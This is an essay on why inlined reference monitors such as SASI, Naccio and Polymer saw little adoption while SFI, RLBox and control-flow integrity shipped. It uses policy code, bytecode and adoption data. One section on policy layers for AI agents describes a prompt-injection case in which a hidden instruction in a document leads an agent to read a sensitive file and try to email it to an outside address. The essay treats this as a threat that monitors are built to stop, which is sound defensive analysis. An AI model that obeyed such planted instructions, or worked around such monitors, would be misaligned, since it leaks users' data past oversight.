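# Why inlined reference monitors saw little production adoption

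## What an inlined reference monitor does

An inlined reference monitor (IRM) enforces a security policy through checks inside a program's code or the libraries it calls. A separate tool, the rewriter, inserts those checks before the code runs. When the program is about to take an action such as reading a file or sending a message, the inserted code checks whether the policy permits the action and stops the program if it does not. Computer scientists at Cornell, MIT, Princeton and Carnegie Mellon built several such systems between 1999 and 2005, but few monitors that enforce freely written policies went into everyday use. The history matters again because developers now put rule checks between AI agents and their tools, and they face many of the same design choices.

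### The monitor in its own address space

The older idea is the plain reference monitor, a component that receives control at every security-relevant action of a program and halts the program when it is about to break a policy. Operating systems contain one. When a program makes a system call to open a file, the processor switches to operating-system code, which checks the user's permissions before opening the file. A reference monitor is useful only if programs cannot bypass or tamper with it and it is small enough for people to verify.

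Hardware usually prevents tampering by giving the monitor its own address space, a region of memory that other programs cannot access. *SASI Enforcement of Security Policies* (Erlingsson and Schneider, 1999) points out that this takes time, because each check forces a context switch, in which the processor suspends the program, runs the monitor and then switches back. *A Language-Based Approach to Security* (Schneider, Morrisett and Harper) adds that the system must copy data between the two address spaces.

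The other drawback is a limited range of events, which are the actions a policy can mention. A monitor in its own address space gains control only when some mechanism, typically a system call, transfers it there, so a policy can cover only the actions that trigger such a transfer. A web browser might need rules about how helper applications use its resources, but those interactions need not involve a system call. Schneider and colleagues give the Melissa and Love Bug viruses as examples. The mail program itself started the script hidden in a message, giving the operating system's kernel no opportunity to intervene. The script then read the address book and mailed out copies of itself with all the user's privileges.

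A check inside the program is a few ordinary instructions, and an event can be anything recognisable in the code. An earlier technique, software fault isolation (SFI), enforced one fixed policy this way, putting a check before each memory access to confine a program to its own region of memory. SASI (Security Automata SFI Implementation) extended the technique to any policy that could be written as a security automaton. Erlingsson and Schneider built two prototypes, one for Intel x86 assembly code and one for Java bytecode, the instructions that the Java virtual machine executes.

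### One policy, from automaton to bytecode

A security automaton is a state machine that takes a program's events in order and rejects the first one for which it has no permitted transition. Erlingsson and Schneider use the policy "no messages sent after reading a file" as their example. It needs two states:

| Current state | File read | Message send | Any other instruction |
|---|---|---|---|
| start | move to hasRead | stay | stay |
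| hasRead | stay | no transition: halt the program | stay |

In SAL, the Security Automaton Language that SASI's users write, the same policy takes a few lines. The comments here are explanatory additions.

```
/* a call to the named method */
MethodCall(name) ::= op=="invokevirtual" && param[1]==name;
/* reading one byte from a file */
FileRead() ::= MethodCall("java/io/FileInputStream/read()I");
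/* writing one byte to the network */
Send() ::= MethodCall("java/net/SocketOutputStream/write(I)V");

start ::=                  /* no file read so far */
    !FileRead() -> start
    FileRead()  -> hasRead
;
hasRead ::=                /* at least one file read */
    !Send() -> hasRead
;
```

The exclamation mark means "not". The state hasRead has no transition for a send, and a missing transition means rejection, so the policy blocks sending in that state without an explicit rule against it.

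Suppose that a Java program contains these two instructions, with other code between them:

```
invokevirtual java/io/FileInputStream/read()I         ; read
...
invokevirtual java/net/SocketOutputStream/write(I)V   ; send
```

After rewriting, the same stretch of program looks like this:

```
ldc 1                                                 ; the number for hasRead
putstatic SASIJVML/state                              ; store it as current state
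invokevirtual java/io/FileInputStream/read()I         ; original read
...
getstatic SASIJVML/state                              ; fetch current state
ifeq SUCCEED                                          ; 0 means start: skip ahead
invokestatic SASIJVML/FAIL()V                         ; otherwise halt
SUCCEED:
invokevirtual java/net/SocketOutputStream/write(I)V   ; original send
```

The rewriter gets from the policy to this code in four steps:

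1. *Insert.* It places a complete copy of the automaton before every instruction in the program.
2. *Evaluate.* It works out each transition condition that the following instruction already settles. Before an addition, for instance, FileRead() and Send() are both false.
3. *Simplify.* It deletes the transitions whose conditions came out false.
4. *Compile.* It turns what remains into bytecode, with a call to FAIL wherever the automaton would reject.

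Before an addition, each state now leads only to itself, so the rewriter adds no code. Before the file read, both states lead to hasRead, since a read is not a send and hasRead permits it. The inserted code can therefore store a 1 without checking the old value. Before the send, start leads back to itself and hasRead has no next state, so the rewriter inserts a test but no update. The inserted code stores the 1 before the read runs, so even a read that ends in an error blocks later sends.

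SASI's rewriter considers only one instruction at a time. If a program reads twice in a row, the rewriter inserts the same store twice, although the second is redundant. Erlingsson and Schneider left out the wider analysis that would remove redundant stores because they did not want to enlarge the software the policy depends on.

In the more general recipe from Schneider and colleagues, an IRM's developer specifies security events (here the two method calls), security state (the stored number) and security updates, which run at an event and change the state or block the action. The policy is separate from the program, so the same policy can be used for many programs, and running the rewriter again adds a second policy.

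Some policies are beyond any monitor that only observes a run and halts it. Schneider and colleagues show that such a monitor can enforce only safety properties, meaning policies whose every violation becomes definite after finitely many steps. In symbols, if Γ is the set of permitted executions and σ is an execution, then

$$\sigma \notin \Gamma \;\Rightarrow\; \exists i\; \forall \tau:\; \sigma[..i]\,\tau \notin \Gamma,$$

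where σ[..i] is the first *i* steps of σ and τ is any continuation. A read followed by a send fits the definition, since nothing the program does later can undo it. "Do not leak the contents of the file" does not. Whether a message leaks the file depends on what the program would have sent had the file been different, and a monitor has only the one run to go on. The SASI example is a stricter substitute for that policy, and it has a price: a mail program that reads its own settings file can never send mail afterwards.

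### Keeping the checks in place

Hardware no longer isolates an inlined monitor's memory, so the monitor needs other protection. Erlingsson and Schneider list three requirements. The program must not be able to change the variables that hold the automaton's state or are used in its conditions. It must not be able to jump around the checks. It also must not alter its own code or bring in code the rewriter hasn't processed, for example through dynamic linking, in which a program loads libraries while it runs.

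Java's type safety meets the first two conditions. The original program cannot access SASI's variables because of their names and types, and verified bytecode can jump only to labelled instructions, none of which are available to it in the inserted code. To meet the third condition, SASI's policies had to forbid dynamic class loading and reflection, which lets a Java program inspect and call classes by name at run time. Polymer, a later system, handles class loading less drastically by rewriting the standard libraries before the virtual machine starts and then each application class as it loads.

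x86 code isn't type-safe, so SASI adds a memory-protection automaton to every policy. The checks inserted for this automaton protect the other inserted checks. This protection depends on the prototype accepting only gcc output, which follows known conventions about registers and branch targets.

### The research line from SASI to Polymer

SASI (1999) was designed to show that one general rewriter could enforce any policy within a monitor's reach, and its distinguishing feature was a check before every machine instruction. Its designers judged neither prototype practical, partly because SAL was awkward to write. Evans and Twyman's *Flexible Policy-Directed Code Safety* (May 1999) presented Naccio, which aimed to make policies portable across platforms. A Naccio author writes rules about abstract resources, such as the number of bytes written to files, and a separate description of the platform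 maps each system call to those resources. The Cornell group's second-generation system was PoET/PSLang, a policy enforcement toolkit with its own specification language. Erlingsson and Schneider's *IRM enforcement of Java stack inspection* (2000) used inlined monitors to reproduce Java's built-in access-control policy; the new idea was to write the monitor's actions as fragments of Java-like code instead of bare automaton states. By June 2005 the problem had become how to combine policies. *Composing Security Policies with Polymer*, by Bauer, Ligatti and Walker, describes a system in which a policy returns a suggestion to ignore the action, allow it, run some other code first, substitute a result, raise an exception or halt. Producing a suggestion has no side effects, so a parent policy can query several others, choose among their suggestions and notify only the policies whose suggestions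 it followed.

### Complete mediation and the trusted computing base

Complete mediation, a term from general computer security, means that the monitor checks every relevant event. Saltzer and Schroeder, in *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems*, made it a design principle in 1975, calling for a check on every access to every object, including accesses during start-up, recovery and maintenance. In an inlined monitor, the rewriter must therefore find every place in the code where an event can occur. Vanoverberghe and Piessens, in *A Caller-Side Inline Reference Monitor for an Object-Oriented Intermediate Language*, call this non-trivial for object-oriented bytecode, where the code that a method call runs can depend on which object receives it.

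Even with a perfect rewriter, the policy has to name the right events. The SAL text above names one method for reading a file, but Java's FileInputStream class has others, which fill a whole array of bytes. A program that used those would stay in the start state and could send whatever it had read.

The trusted computing base (TCB) is all the software that must be correct for the policy to hold; the US standards agency NIST also includes hardware and firmware in its glossary definition. A small TCB was a main selling point of inlining. For the Java version of SASI, Erlingsson and Schneider count roughly 1,600 lines for the SAL parser, 1,600 for the code that evaluates and simplifies conditions, and 1,000 for the SAL compiler. An assembler and a disassembler add 3,950 more, but any Java virtual machine already relies on such components. Because SASI works on bytecode, a bug in the Java compiler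 cannot break the policy. Schneider and colleagues contrast this kind of figure with the millions of lines in Windows 2000. The comparison slightly favors inlining, since the rewritten program still runs on a virtual machine and an operating system, and a serious flaw in either could defeat the checks.

### AI agents, tool calls and agent policy layers

An AI agent is a program in which a language model chooses the actions. The model only produces output such as text. Surrounding software, often called the harness, interprets part of that output as a request to use a tool, runs the tool and returns the result to the model, which then chooses the next step. *Efficient and Sound Probabilistic Verification for AI Agents* (2026) defines such a request, called a tool call, as a tool's identifier and the arguments for that particular use, such as "send email" with a recipient and a body. In *Ring-0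 by Default* (2026), Li, Huang and colleagues compare the tool call to a system call because it is the fixed interface through which the agent reaches files, processes and networks.

An agent policy layer is software that checks an agent's proposed tool calls against rules before they run. *Agenra* (2026) divides the work in a typical way. The application installs the rules for a user's task, the agent proposes calls, and a reference monitor checks them. The agent cannot change the rules. The designers assume that an attacker may have planted instructions in a document or message that the agent reads (prompt injection), so the rules have to hold even when the agent deliberately proposes a forbidden call. A blocked call seldom ends the run, whereas under SASI it would. In *Efficient and Sound Probabilistic Verification for AI Agents*, the monitor suspends the call, computes the state that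 would follow and tests it against the policy. If the test fails, the monitor discards the computed state and returns an explanation so that the agent can try something else.

Palumbo, Choudhary and colleagues (2026), in *Formal Policy Enforcement for Agentic Systems*, work through a case very close to SASI's. A user asks an agent to summarise a vendor's document. The document contains a hidden instruction, the agent goes on to read a sensitive internal file, and then it tries to email an outside address. SASI's automaton would stop that email. It would also stop the agent from mailing the user the summary, since any summary comes after a read. Palumbo and colleagues instead record which earlier messages and results may have influenced each action, and write the policy in Datalog, a logic language that originated in database work:

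```
Deny(a) :- ExternalSend(a), Tainted(a), HasSecret(a).
```

The rule blocks an action if it sends data outside and depends on both untrusted input and sensitive data. It is far more selective than "no messages sent after reading a file", but the monitor needs much more information to enforce it, namely which tools send data outside, which files are sensitive and what the agent had read before each call.

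Most agent policy layers sit outside the model and beside the tools. *ConfGuard* (2026) describes a deterministic policy outside the model as the dominant pattern of defence. *Sapien* (2026), for example, hooks into the harness between agent and tools and checks every call the agent proposes. Inlining in SASI's sense is hardly possible here, because a neural network contains no "send" instruction that a rewriter could put a check before. Like inlined monitors, agent policy layers must know which events matter, with what arguments and after what history, but their checks run outside the model.

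A monitor placed beside the tools also misses some actions. Li, Chen and colleagues (2026) acknowledge in *VIGIL* that their monitor cannot observe what a script does inside a single tool call. For this reason, *AgentBouncer* (2026) intercepts the system calls that a tool makes while it runs, so it can block one harmful action inside a tool and let the harmless ones proceed.

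## Which inlined monitors reached production

A monitor has reached production when people who had no part in building it run it in their ordinary work, it is on by default or an organisation has deliberately turned it on, and someone keeps it working as the software around it changes. This excludes demonstrations, compiler options that nobody sets, and products that their makers have dropped.

Whether a monitor meets these conditions depends a lot on where its policy comes from. Configurable monitors, such as SASI, PoET/PSLang, Naccio and Polymer, enforce whatever policy someone writes for them. Fixed-policy monitors enforce one built-in policy, so their users don't write any.

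### What became of the four research systems

Erlingsson and Schneider put demonstrations of both SASI prototypes on the web, but did not feel that either could "become a practical tool". They found SAL awkward because it stored everything a policy must remember in the automaton's current state, which cannot hold a string, so it was hard to require that a program use the same string throughout a series of operations. They also complained that events were hard to identify in x86 code, which has no explicit functions, only instruction sequences that look like function calls. To find these, a policy author had to embed something like a disassembler in each policy.

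No production user of PoET/PSLang, the SASI designers' second system, is known. This lack of evidence is a weaker basis for a conclusion than the designers' own verdict on SASI.

Naccio's home page, University of Virginia's *Policy-Directed Code Safety* (2000), lists its last update as 1 October 2000. It offers papers, slides, a library of policies and a public challenge to break the system, but mentions no users of the system. Some companies had heard of Naccio, because the project gave its seminar talk at AT&T, Compaq, IBM, Lucent, Microsoft Research and several universities in the spring of 1999.

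Polymer was available from a Princeton project page, according to a lecture slide in DePaul University's *Security Automata*. The fullest account of its use is in *Policy Enforcement via Program Monitoring* (2006), by Ligatti, one of its designers. He and his colleagues wrote a large policy for email programs and tested it on Pooka, a mail client of about 50,000 lines, without changing Pooka's source code. This was a serious trial but still a demonstration, with one rule sending a blind copy of every outgoing message to a demo address at Princeton.

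On the public record, all four systems fail the first condition, though a company could have used any of them internally without announcing it. People in the field seem to have agreed. Two decades after SASI, Xu (2020), in *Native Software Security Hardening in the Real World*, was still trying to narrow the gap between theory and practice for inlined monitors.

### Software fault isolation

SFI, the technique that SASI generalised, confines the jumps of untrusted code as well as its reads and writes. Suppose the untrusted code contains an x86 instruction that copies a register into an element of an array called `dirty`. MiSFIT, a specialised SFI tool from the 1990s, replaces that instruction with these six (the comments are explanatory additions):

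```
pushl %ebx                   ; free a register
leal  dirty(,%eax,4), %ebx   ; work out the target address
andl  offsetMask, %ebx       ; keep only the position within a region
orl   writeSegment, %ebx     ; fill in the code's own region
movl  %edx, (%ebx)           ; write there
popl  %ebx                   ; restore the register
```

An address outside the region raises no alarm. The two masking instructions turn it into some address inside, where the write can damage only the untrusted code's own data. SASI can enforce the same policy, but it keeps the original write and puts a test in front:

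```
pushl %ebx
leal  dirty(,%eax,4), %ebx
andl  segmentMask, %ebx      ; keep only the region
cmpl  writeSegment, %ebx     ; is it the code's own?
jne   SASIx86_FAIL           ; if not, halt
popl  %ebx
movl  %edx, dirty(,%eax,4)   ; original write
```

With either tool, the policy is the same for every program and nobody has to write it.

SFI reached ordinary users through web browsers. Google's Native Client used it to run compiled code from websites inside Chrome. Native Client met all three conditions for some years, then failed the third when Google deprecated it. WebAssembly, a portable instruction format that also confines each module to its own memory, runs in all major browsers and has remained in use after Native Client's deprecation.

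Firefox also uses WebAssembly to isolate parts of the browser from one another. A browser contains many third-party libraries, such as libjpeg for displaying JPEG images, and a memory bug in one of them can give an attacker control of the whole browser process. *RLBox*, by Narayan, Disselkoen and colleagues, compiles such a library to WebAssembly so that the damage stays within the library's own memory.

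Narayan and colleagues found that sandboxing libjpeg in its own region of memory was not enough to protect Firefox. Firefox takes the size of an image from libjpeg and then copies that much data into a buffer of its own. A hijacked libjpeg can give a false size and make Firefox overrun the buffer, without itself touching memory outside its region. RLBox, a C++ library, gives every value that comes out of the sandbox a "tainted" type, and code that uses a tainted value unchecked does not compile. The developer has to write the missing check, for instance that the size is no larger than the buffer. Narayan and colleagues report that these checks took two to four lines of code on average.

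Firefox shipped with one library sandboxed by RLBox in February 2020, on Mac and Linux. By December 2021 it had five, and the sandboxing extended to Windows and Android. Users got the sandboxing without doing anything, so RLBox counts as production adoption. Only part of its policy is fixed, however. The rule about memory is built in, but someone had to decide and write down what counts as sensible output from each library.

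### Control-flow integrity

Programs often call a function through an address stored in memory. Houy and Bartel, in *Twenty years later*, give the example of a login program that stores such an address directly after the space for the user's password. Anyone who types a password that is too long overwrites the address, and so can choose what the program runs next. Control-flow integrity (CFI) puts a check before the call, which in simplified form looks like this:

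```
mov    rax, [rbp-0x8]     ; the address about to be called
movabs rcx, typeid_auth   ; the permitted target
cmp    rax, rcx
je     check_passed
ud2                       ; illegal instruction: crash
check_passed:
call   rax
```

The compiler inserts the check and also works out which targets to permit. In LLVM, the compiler framework that includes the C and C++ compiler Clang, these are the functions with the same parameter and return types as the intended one. CFI is therefore an inlined reference monitor in the full sense. Its events are indirect calls, the compiler is its rewriter, and the policy comes out of the program's own types. (A second kind of CFI protects the return from a function. The figures below are for calls.)

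Martín Abadi, Mihai Budiu, Úlfar Erlingsson and Jay Ligatti introduced CFI, the fixed-policy monitor that later shipped, in 2005. Erlingsson also helped design SASI, and Ligatti helped design Polymer. Versions of CFI for the GCC and LLVM compilers followed in 2014. Microsoft released its own version, Control Flow Guard, the same year, and Android began using LLVM's in 2018.

CFI adoption since then has varied widely by platform. Houy and Bartel ran SeeCFI, their tool for finding the inserted checks in compiled files, on 102 Android and Linux system images containing about 610,000 binaries. On Google's Android images, the share of C and C++ binaries with call protection rose from about 7% in Android 10 to 28.7% in Android 13, released in 2022. That year, the share was 0.22% on Debian and 0.08% on Ubuntu, with no upward trend. They found no binaries that used GCC's version. GCC's standard build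 leaves the feature out, so a developer who wants it must rebuild the compiler.

Becker, Hollick and Classen (2024), in *SoK*, examined two Windows builds and 33 Android images from seven vendors. On Windows, only 2.63% of files lacked protection. On Google's Pixel 7, 7% of executables, 17% of libraries and all 241 kernel modules (the loadable parts of the operating system's core) were protected. By those counts, 29% of files were protected, or 15% without the kernel modules. The 29% figure is close to SeeCFI's, so much of Android's apparent progress may come from the kernel. Samsung, Oppo and Vivo phones had similarly low coverage of executables and libraries. Coverage was much higher on the Xiaomi 13, at 48% of executables and 65% of libraries, which is hard to reconcile with the study's summary that under 17% of files in recent firmware have protection.

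The protection is also weaker than its coverage suggests. LLVM's scheme cannot check calls into unprotected libraries, so it allows them. Becker and colleagues found that every protected executable they examined on Android depended on at least one such library, and they conclude that this makes the enforcement ineffective. CFI on Android still meets the conditions for adoption, since it runs by default on a very large number of phones.

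More recent work describes similar adoption. *A Practical Guideline and Taxonomy to LLVM's Control Flow Integrity* (Houy, Kreyssig et al., 2025) calls adoption inconsistent, with Android and Windows ahead, Linux struggling, and limited support in the open-source browsers Chromium and Firefox. It also reports tests of published exploits for four known vulnerabilities on programs compiled with and without CFI, in which CFI blocked two of the four. A February 2026 announcement from Umeå University, *Advanced security technology rarely used*, still puts the share of Linux packages with CFI below 1%, but reports no new count.

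The same announcement reports that when Houy's group tried to turn on CFI in OpenJDK, the open-source version of Java, the software failed to compile, crashed or behaved unpredictably. C programmers often call a function through a pointer of a slightly different type, or load plug-ins that the compiler did not process. These programs work without CFI, but CFI treats such calls as attacks and stops the program.

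Houy, Kreyssig and Bartel (2025) try to automate the repair with *CFIghter*, a tool that runs a project's own tests, finds the false alarms and adds narrow exceptions to the policy. In util-linux, a large collection of basic Linux utilities, it removed 95.8% of the false alarms and kept strict checking at over 89% of indirect call sites. Without such a tool, developers have to find and write the exceptions by hand, so even a fixed policy can leave them some policy to write.

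### Fixed policies shipped, and freely written ones mostly did not

The table applies the three conditions to each case.

| Monitor | Policy | Ordinary users run it | On by default or by decision | Maintained |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| SASI | configurable | no, demonstrations only | no | no, its designers moved on to a successor |
| PoET/PSLang | configurable | none known | none known | no sign of it |
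| Naccio | configurable | none known | none known | project page last updated in 2000 |
| Polymer | configurable | none known | none known | no sign of it |
| Native Client | fixed | yes | yes, in Chrome | until Google deprecated it |
| WebAssembly | fixed | yes | yes, in browsers | yes |
| RLBox in Firefox | fixed, plus hand-written checks | yes | yes | yes |
| CFI on Windows | fixed | yes | yes | yes |
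| CFI on Android | fixed | yes | yes, for part of the system | yes |
| CFI on Debian and Ubuntu | fixed | barely | no, for nearly all programs | yes, in LLVM |

The last row shows that a fixed policy doesn't guarantee adoption, though it seems to make adoption much easier. Debian's developers had the same compiler and ready-made policy as Android's but hardly used them. Houy and Bartel point out that Android's developers extended and patched LLVM's version of CFI until programs stopped crashing, while on Linux the decision falls largely to the developers of each application. Concern for security doesn't fully explain adoption either, since GrapheneOS, an Android variant built for security and privacy, has almost exactly the same CFI coverage on the Pixel 7 as Google's own system.

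The high coverage in Windows suggests that a looser policy may also be easier to ship. Control Flow Guard lets an indirect call go to any function that the program has marked as a possible target, whatever its type. This rule is weaker than LLVM's and blocks far fewer legitimate calls. But Microsoft also compiles all of Windows itself, which could explain the high coverage instead.

The two groups in the table also differ in whether the software's makers or its recipients apply the monitor. Becker and colleagues found that every CFI scheme in use works through the compiler, and Firefox's developers also compile their sandboxed libraries themselves. In these cases the people who make the software insert the checks and can fix whatever breaks. SASI's Java version, Naccio and Polymer were for people who received a compiled program they did not trust. Those people had to choose a policy for a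 program they had not written, and could do little if it then stopped working. The difference between fixed and configurable policies therefore partly overlaps with the difference between makers and recipients, and ten cases are too few to separate their effects.

Some configurable monitors have succeeded. The search servers Elasticsearch, OpenSearch and Solr adopted inlined monitors in 2025 and 2026, and some employers add checks they choose to the apps on their staff's phones.

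Commercial products are harder to classify. Several security companies sell software that inserts checks into Java or .NET bytecode, usually under the name runtime application self-protection. A customer who keeps such a product switched on and set to block attacks would satisfy all three conditions, but it is hard to establish how many do so without relying on the vendors' claims. Becker and colleagues left commercial CFI products out of their study for a similar reason. Even wide use would be an exception to the pattern only where customers write their own rules, because a product that enforces only the vendor's rules is close to a fixed-policy monitor.

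There seems to be no systematic survey of the adoption of configurable inlined monitors. Researchers can measure CFI adoption by scanning a system image and counting the files that contain the checks, but that method does not work for tools whose inserted code differs with every policy. The evidence that those tools failed is therefore still limited to a handful of papers and project pages.

### Speed as a rival explanation

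The research monitors may also have seen little adoption because they were too slow. This explanation can be tested in the same way as the other proposed causes. A cause of low adoption should be present where adoption failed and absent or overcome where it succeeded, and the people who made the decision should have named it. The last condition is hard to meet because people who never installed Polymer did not write down why. The best substitutes are the designers' own verdicts and reports from engineers who had trouble using a monitor.

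SASI slowed programs down. Erlingsson and Schneider ran three programs under SASI and under MiSFIT, 30 times each on a 266 MHz Pentium II. In the table, 1 is the running time of the unmodified program.

| Program | MiSFIT | SASI | Extra time for SASI over MiSFIT |
|---|---|---|---|
| Page-eviction hotlist | 2.378 | 3.643 | 53% |
| Logical log-structured disk | 1.576 | 1.654 | 5% |
| MD5 message digest | 1.331 | 1.363 | 2% |

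On two of the programs, the general-purpose SASI was nearly as fast as the specialised MiSFIT. It did much worse on the hotlist, which uses memory intensively. Erlingsson and Schneider concede that MiSFIT is considerably faster on some other programs too, and they expected better optimisation of SASI's inserted code to help. The experiment measured SASI enforcing only its memory-protection policy, which keeps the monitor itself safe on x86. Any policy that a user wrote would have added further overhead.

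The Java prototype better shows how much overhead a policy itself adds, because Java's type safety already protects the monitor. Erlingsson and Schneider used it to reproduce Java 1.1's SecurityManager, the built-in component that decides whether a program may, for example, open a file. Their SAL policy was about four pages long and called the same check functions at the same points in the Java libraries. In small benchmarks, they found no statistical difference in overhead between the two. They thought SASI might be faster in practice, because its rewriter can omit checks that are certain to succeed, whereas Sun's version always ran them. Using benchmark data from Naccio, they estimated that this could make some programs up to four times faster.

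Polymer's figures are more mixed. Its rewriter took 107 seconds to process all 28,742 methods in the standard Java libraries, or 3.7 milliseconds per method. The libraries need rewriting only once, because the rewriter inserts general hooks rather than a particular policy, so a user can change the policy without rewriting anything. Loading one of the application's own classes took 12 milliseconds on average, twice as long as normal. Each transfer of control to the policy and back added about 0.62 milliseconds.

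Ligatti calls this last overhead very low, and it is for an email program. He reports that the overhead in Pooka was rarely noticeable, but it would add up for frequent events. If a program read a one-megabyte file one byte at a time and a policy checked each read, the transfers alone would take about eleven minutes. Polymer would therefore have been too slow for some purposes, but not for the kind of program its designers had in mind.

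The monitors that shipped also slowed programs down. In tests by Narayan and colleagues, sandboxing made JPEG rendering 26% to 33% slower, depending on image size. Font rendering was 82% slower with WebAssembly in 2020 and still 35% slower in 2021, after they had optimised the switch into and out of the sandbox. Mozilla's developers measured slowdowns of 7% for parsing XML and 10.5% for decompressing fonts. These slowdowns affect one component rather than the whole browser, which makes them easier to accept. They are still in the same range as SASI's 36% on MD5, and Firefox shipped with sandboxed libraries anyway. By contrast, LLVM's CFI checks add little overhead, but Debian and Ubuntu barely use them.

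The people closest to the decisions mostly gave reasons other than runtime overhead. Erlingsson and Schneider blamed SASI's policy language and its events. Trail of Bits, a security firm, had publicly recommended CFI and wanted to follow its own advice. Its engineers planned to add CFI to osquery, a Facebook program they knew well, and compare Clang's version with Microsoft's. They never got as far as the comparison, and *The Challenges of Deploying Security Mitigations* (2017) instead discusses development effort and ease of use. Houy and Bartel do list overhead among the possible reasons for CFI's low uptake, but part of that overhead is the extra memory and processor time LLVM needs to link a program with CFI. That part falls on the developer at build time, before any user runs the program.

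## The work of writing a complete policy

A configurable monitor protects nobody until someone has written down what it should stop, and that may take more work than the protection is worth. The argument rests on four premises:

1. A policy stops only the events it names.
2. A large library offers many routes to the same effect, such as reading a file.
3. Few people know all of those routes.
4. Most users will not pay for the time and expertise it takes to find them.

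If so, fixed-policy monitors did better because their users don't have to write a policy. Úlfar Erlingsson, who helped design both SASI and CFI, takes roughly this view in *Data-driven Software Security* (2016), where he says defences against memory corruption are used almost everywhere because users specify no policy for them. He gives no data for this, and CFI's record on Linux shows that a ready-made policy doesn't guarantee adoption.

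### The reads that SASI's example misses

SASI's example policy, "no messages sent after reading a file", recognises a read by looking for an instruction that names one method. Java's standard library already had several other ways to read a file in 1999:

| Call in the program | What it reads | Does the policy notice? |
|---|---|---|
| `FileInputStream.read()` | one byte | yes |
| `FileInputStream.read(byte[])` | enough bytes to fill an array, if available | no |
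| `FileInputStream.read(byte[], int, int)` | bytes for part of an array | no |
| `RandomAccessFile.read()`, `readLine()`, `readInt()` and others | data from any position in a file | no |
| `FileReader.read()` | one character of text | no |
| `InputStream.read()` on a FileInputStream object | one byte | no |

The last row is easy to overlook, because it runs the very method that the policy names:

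```
InputStream in = new FileInputStream("secrets.txt");
int b = in.read();
```

FileInputStream is a subclass of InputStream, and the programmer has declared the variable as an InputStream. The Java compiler writes the declared type into the bytecode, so the instruction names `InputStream.read()`. At run time the variable holds a FileInputStream, so the virtual machine runs that class's `read()` method. SASI's policy checks only the name in the instruction, so it doesn't match the call. The policy can miss sends for the same reason, since a Java program normally receives a socket's output stream as a plain OutputStream and doesn't need to name the class that the policy looks for.

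Erlingsson and Schneider used the example to show SAL's notation, not as a finished policy. SAL policies can access the state of the virtual machine, so a policy writer could write a more careful test. A cruder fix would count every `InputStream.read()` as a file read, but then a program that had read from the keyboard or the network could no longer send messages.

Some routes don't look like reads. Evans and Twyman mention an attack on earlier versions of Java in which programs exploited the library's font loading to access restricted information. A policy author who searched the documentation for methods called "read" would have missed this route.

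David Evans points out in his doctoral thesis on Naccio that Java code can reach files, the network and the display only through native methods, which are written outside Java. Sun's JDK 1.1.6, the version he studied, had 567 of them. Checks on native methods would cover every public method that calls them, including ones the policy's author has never heard of. But a call to a native method that opens a file gives little indication of why the file is needed. The font loader and a hostile program make the same call, so a policy that stops the hostile program also stops the font loader unless the monitor can identify the caller.

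### Listing what is allowed

A policy author can also avoid the first premise by listing the permitted events and blocking all others. Forgetting a method then blocks some legitimate work but lets no attack through. SASI's automata already reject anything without a transition, but the example policy loses this advantage because a single transition permits every instruction except a send.

The policy's author has to know everything the program legitimately does, and often someone else wrote the program. Mistakes in the policy also show up at once, because the program stops working. Evans and Twyman cite anecdotal evidence that users quickly disable any safety system that burdens them, because they benefit from it only in the rare case that a program is dangerous.

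"All others" also means all other events that the monitor can intercept. Naccio's strictest test policy, DisallowAll, forbids every operation on every resource Naccio covers. It still can't limit memory or processor time, because a program uses those without calling the library.

### The odds of finding every method

An illustrative calculation shows how demanding completeness is. Suppose that 200 library methods can produce the effect a policy forbids, and that the author catches each one with probability 0.99, independently of the others. The probability of catching all of them is

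$$0.99^{200} \approx 0.13.$$

This very careful author misses two methods on average and writes a complete policy only 13% of the time. To have a 95% chance of writing a complete one, the author would have to miss no more than about one method in 3,900.

Two hundred is a realistic rough figure for a broad policy. To enforce DisallowAll, Evans had to wrap 182 library routines in checking code, including 21 that every policy must wrap to protect the monitor itself. His narrower LimitWrite policy, which forbids changes to existing files and caps the amount of data written, needed 59 beyond those 21. If the chance of finding each routine is again 0.99, the chance of finding all 59 is about 55%.

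The weak assumption here is that omissions are independent. A policy writer who remembers one `read` method of FileInputStream will probably look up the other two, while one who forgets RandomAccessFile will miss all its methods. If the 200 methods came in 40 groups of five, and the writer caught or missed whole groups, the chance of a complete policy would rise to 67%, but each omission would leave five methods unchecked.

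How much an omission matters depends on the threat. An attacker can search for an unguarded method, so a policy that covers 198 of the 200 may be worth little. But if a buggy program's mistakes fall more or less at random, the same policy catches nearly all of them. Evans and Twyman also wanted to guard against mistakes. They wrote a policy for the archiving tool tar that stops the mistyped command `tar cf *`, which would otherwise overwrite the first file in the directory with an archive of the rest. Completeness therefore matters much more for hostile code, which most of these systems were built to handle, than for careless code.

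Naccio's history suggests that experts do miss methods. In the paper of May 1999, LimitWrite's rule against changing existing files covered three operations: opening a file for writing, opening it for appending and deleting it. In Evans's thesis of October 1999, the corresponding rule covered ten. The number of wrapped routines, excluding those that protect the monitor, rose from 13 to 59. Some of this growth came from dividing operations more finely and from bookkeeping, such as tracking file names for error messages. But the file operations printed in the May paper do not include renaming, and renaming one file onto another can destroy the second. Unless Naccio reported a rename as some other operation, a program could have used it to replace an existing file despite the policy.

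### What the policy has to remember

Besides finding the events, a policy writer often has to keep track of what happened earlier. SAL's single current state is enough for a yes-or-no fact such as "has read a file".

A policy might instead let a program delete only files it has created itself. The monitor then has to record the names of those files, and because a SAL state can't hold a string, the direct way is to write one state for each possible name. If names have up to eight lower-case letters, that takes about 217 billion states, even for a program that creates only one file. If the policy writer knows the names in advance, the policy needs fewer states, but the number doubles with each additional file. Ten files take 1,024 states, one for each combination the program might have created.

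Counting causes the same problem. Naccio's LimitWrite policy allows a program to write up to a million bytes and keeps count in an integer variable. A version written as plain states would need about a million of them just to keep count.

Erlingsson and Schneider proposed adding typed variables to the monitor's memory, which would remove the difficulty. Naccio already had such variables, and Polymer's policies are Java objects that can store whatever Java can. However, systems that process their policies with a Java compiler add the compiler to their trusted computing base, which SASI's designers had avoided. SAL's awkwardness explains why SASI itself went no further, but not why its successors also saw little adoption, since other systems had solved the language problem by 1999.

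### Describing the library once

A policy can be short once someone has identified the events it covers. SASI's version of Java's SecurityManager could fit in four pages because Sun's engineers had already decided which points in the library needed checks.

Naccio turned this into a method: all its policies share one description of the library, called the platform interface. This is the entry for Java's method for deleting a file, with explanatory comments added:

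```
wrapper boolean delete () {
  RFileSystem.preDelete (rfile);    // run any checks on deleting
  #;                                // the original method runs here
  if (result) {                     // if the deletion succeeded,
    RFileSystem.postDelete (rfile); // run any checks that follow it
  }
}
```

To stop a program from creating or altering files, a policy author only has to attach a violation to one group of operations, `RFileSystem.modifyFile`, and Naccio works out which library calls need checks. It leaves the other calls unchanged, so they have no added run-time overhead.

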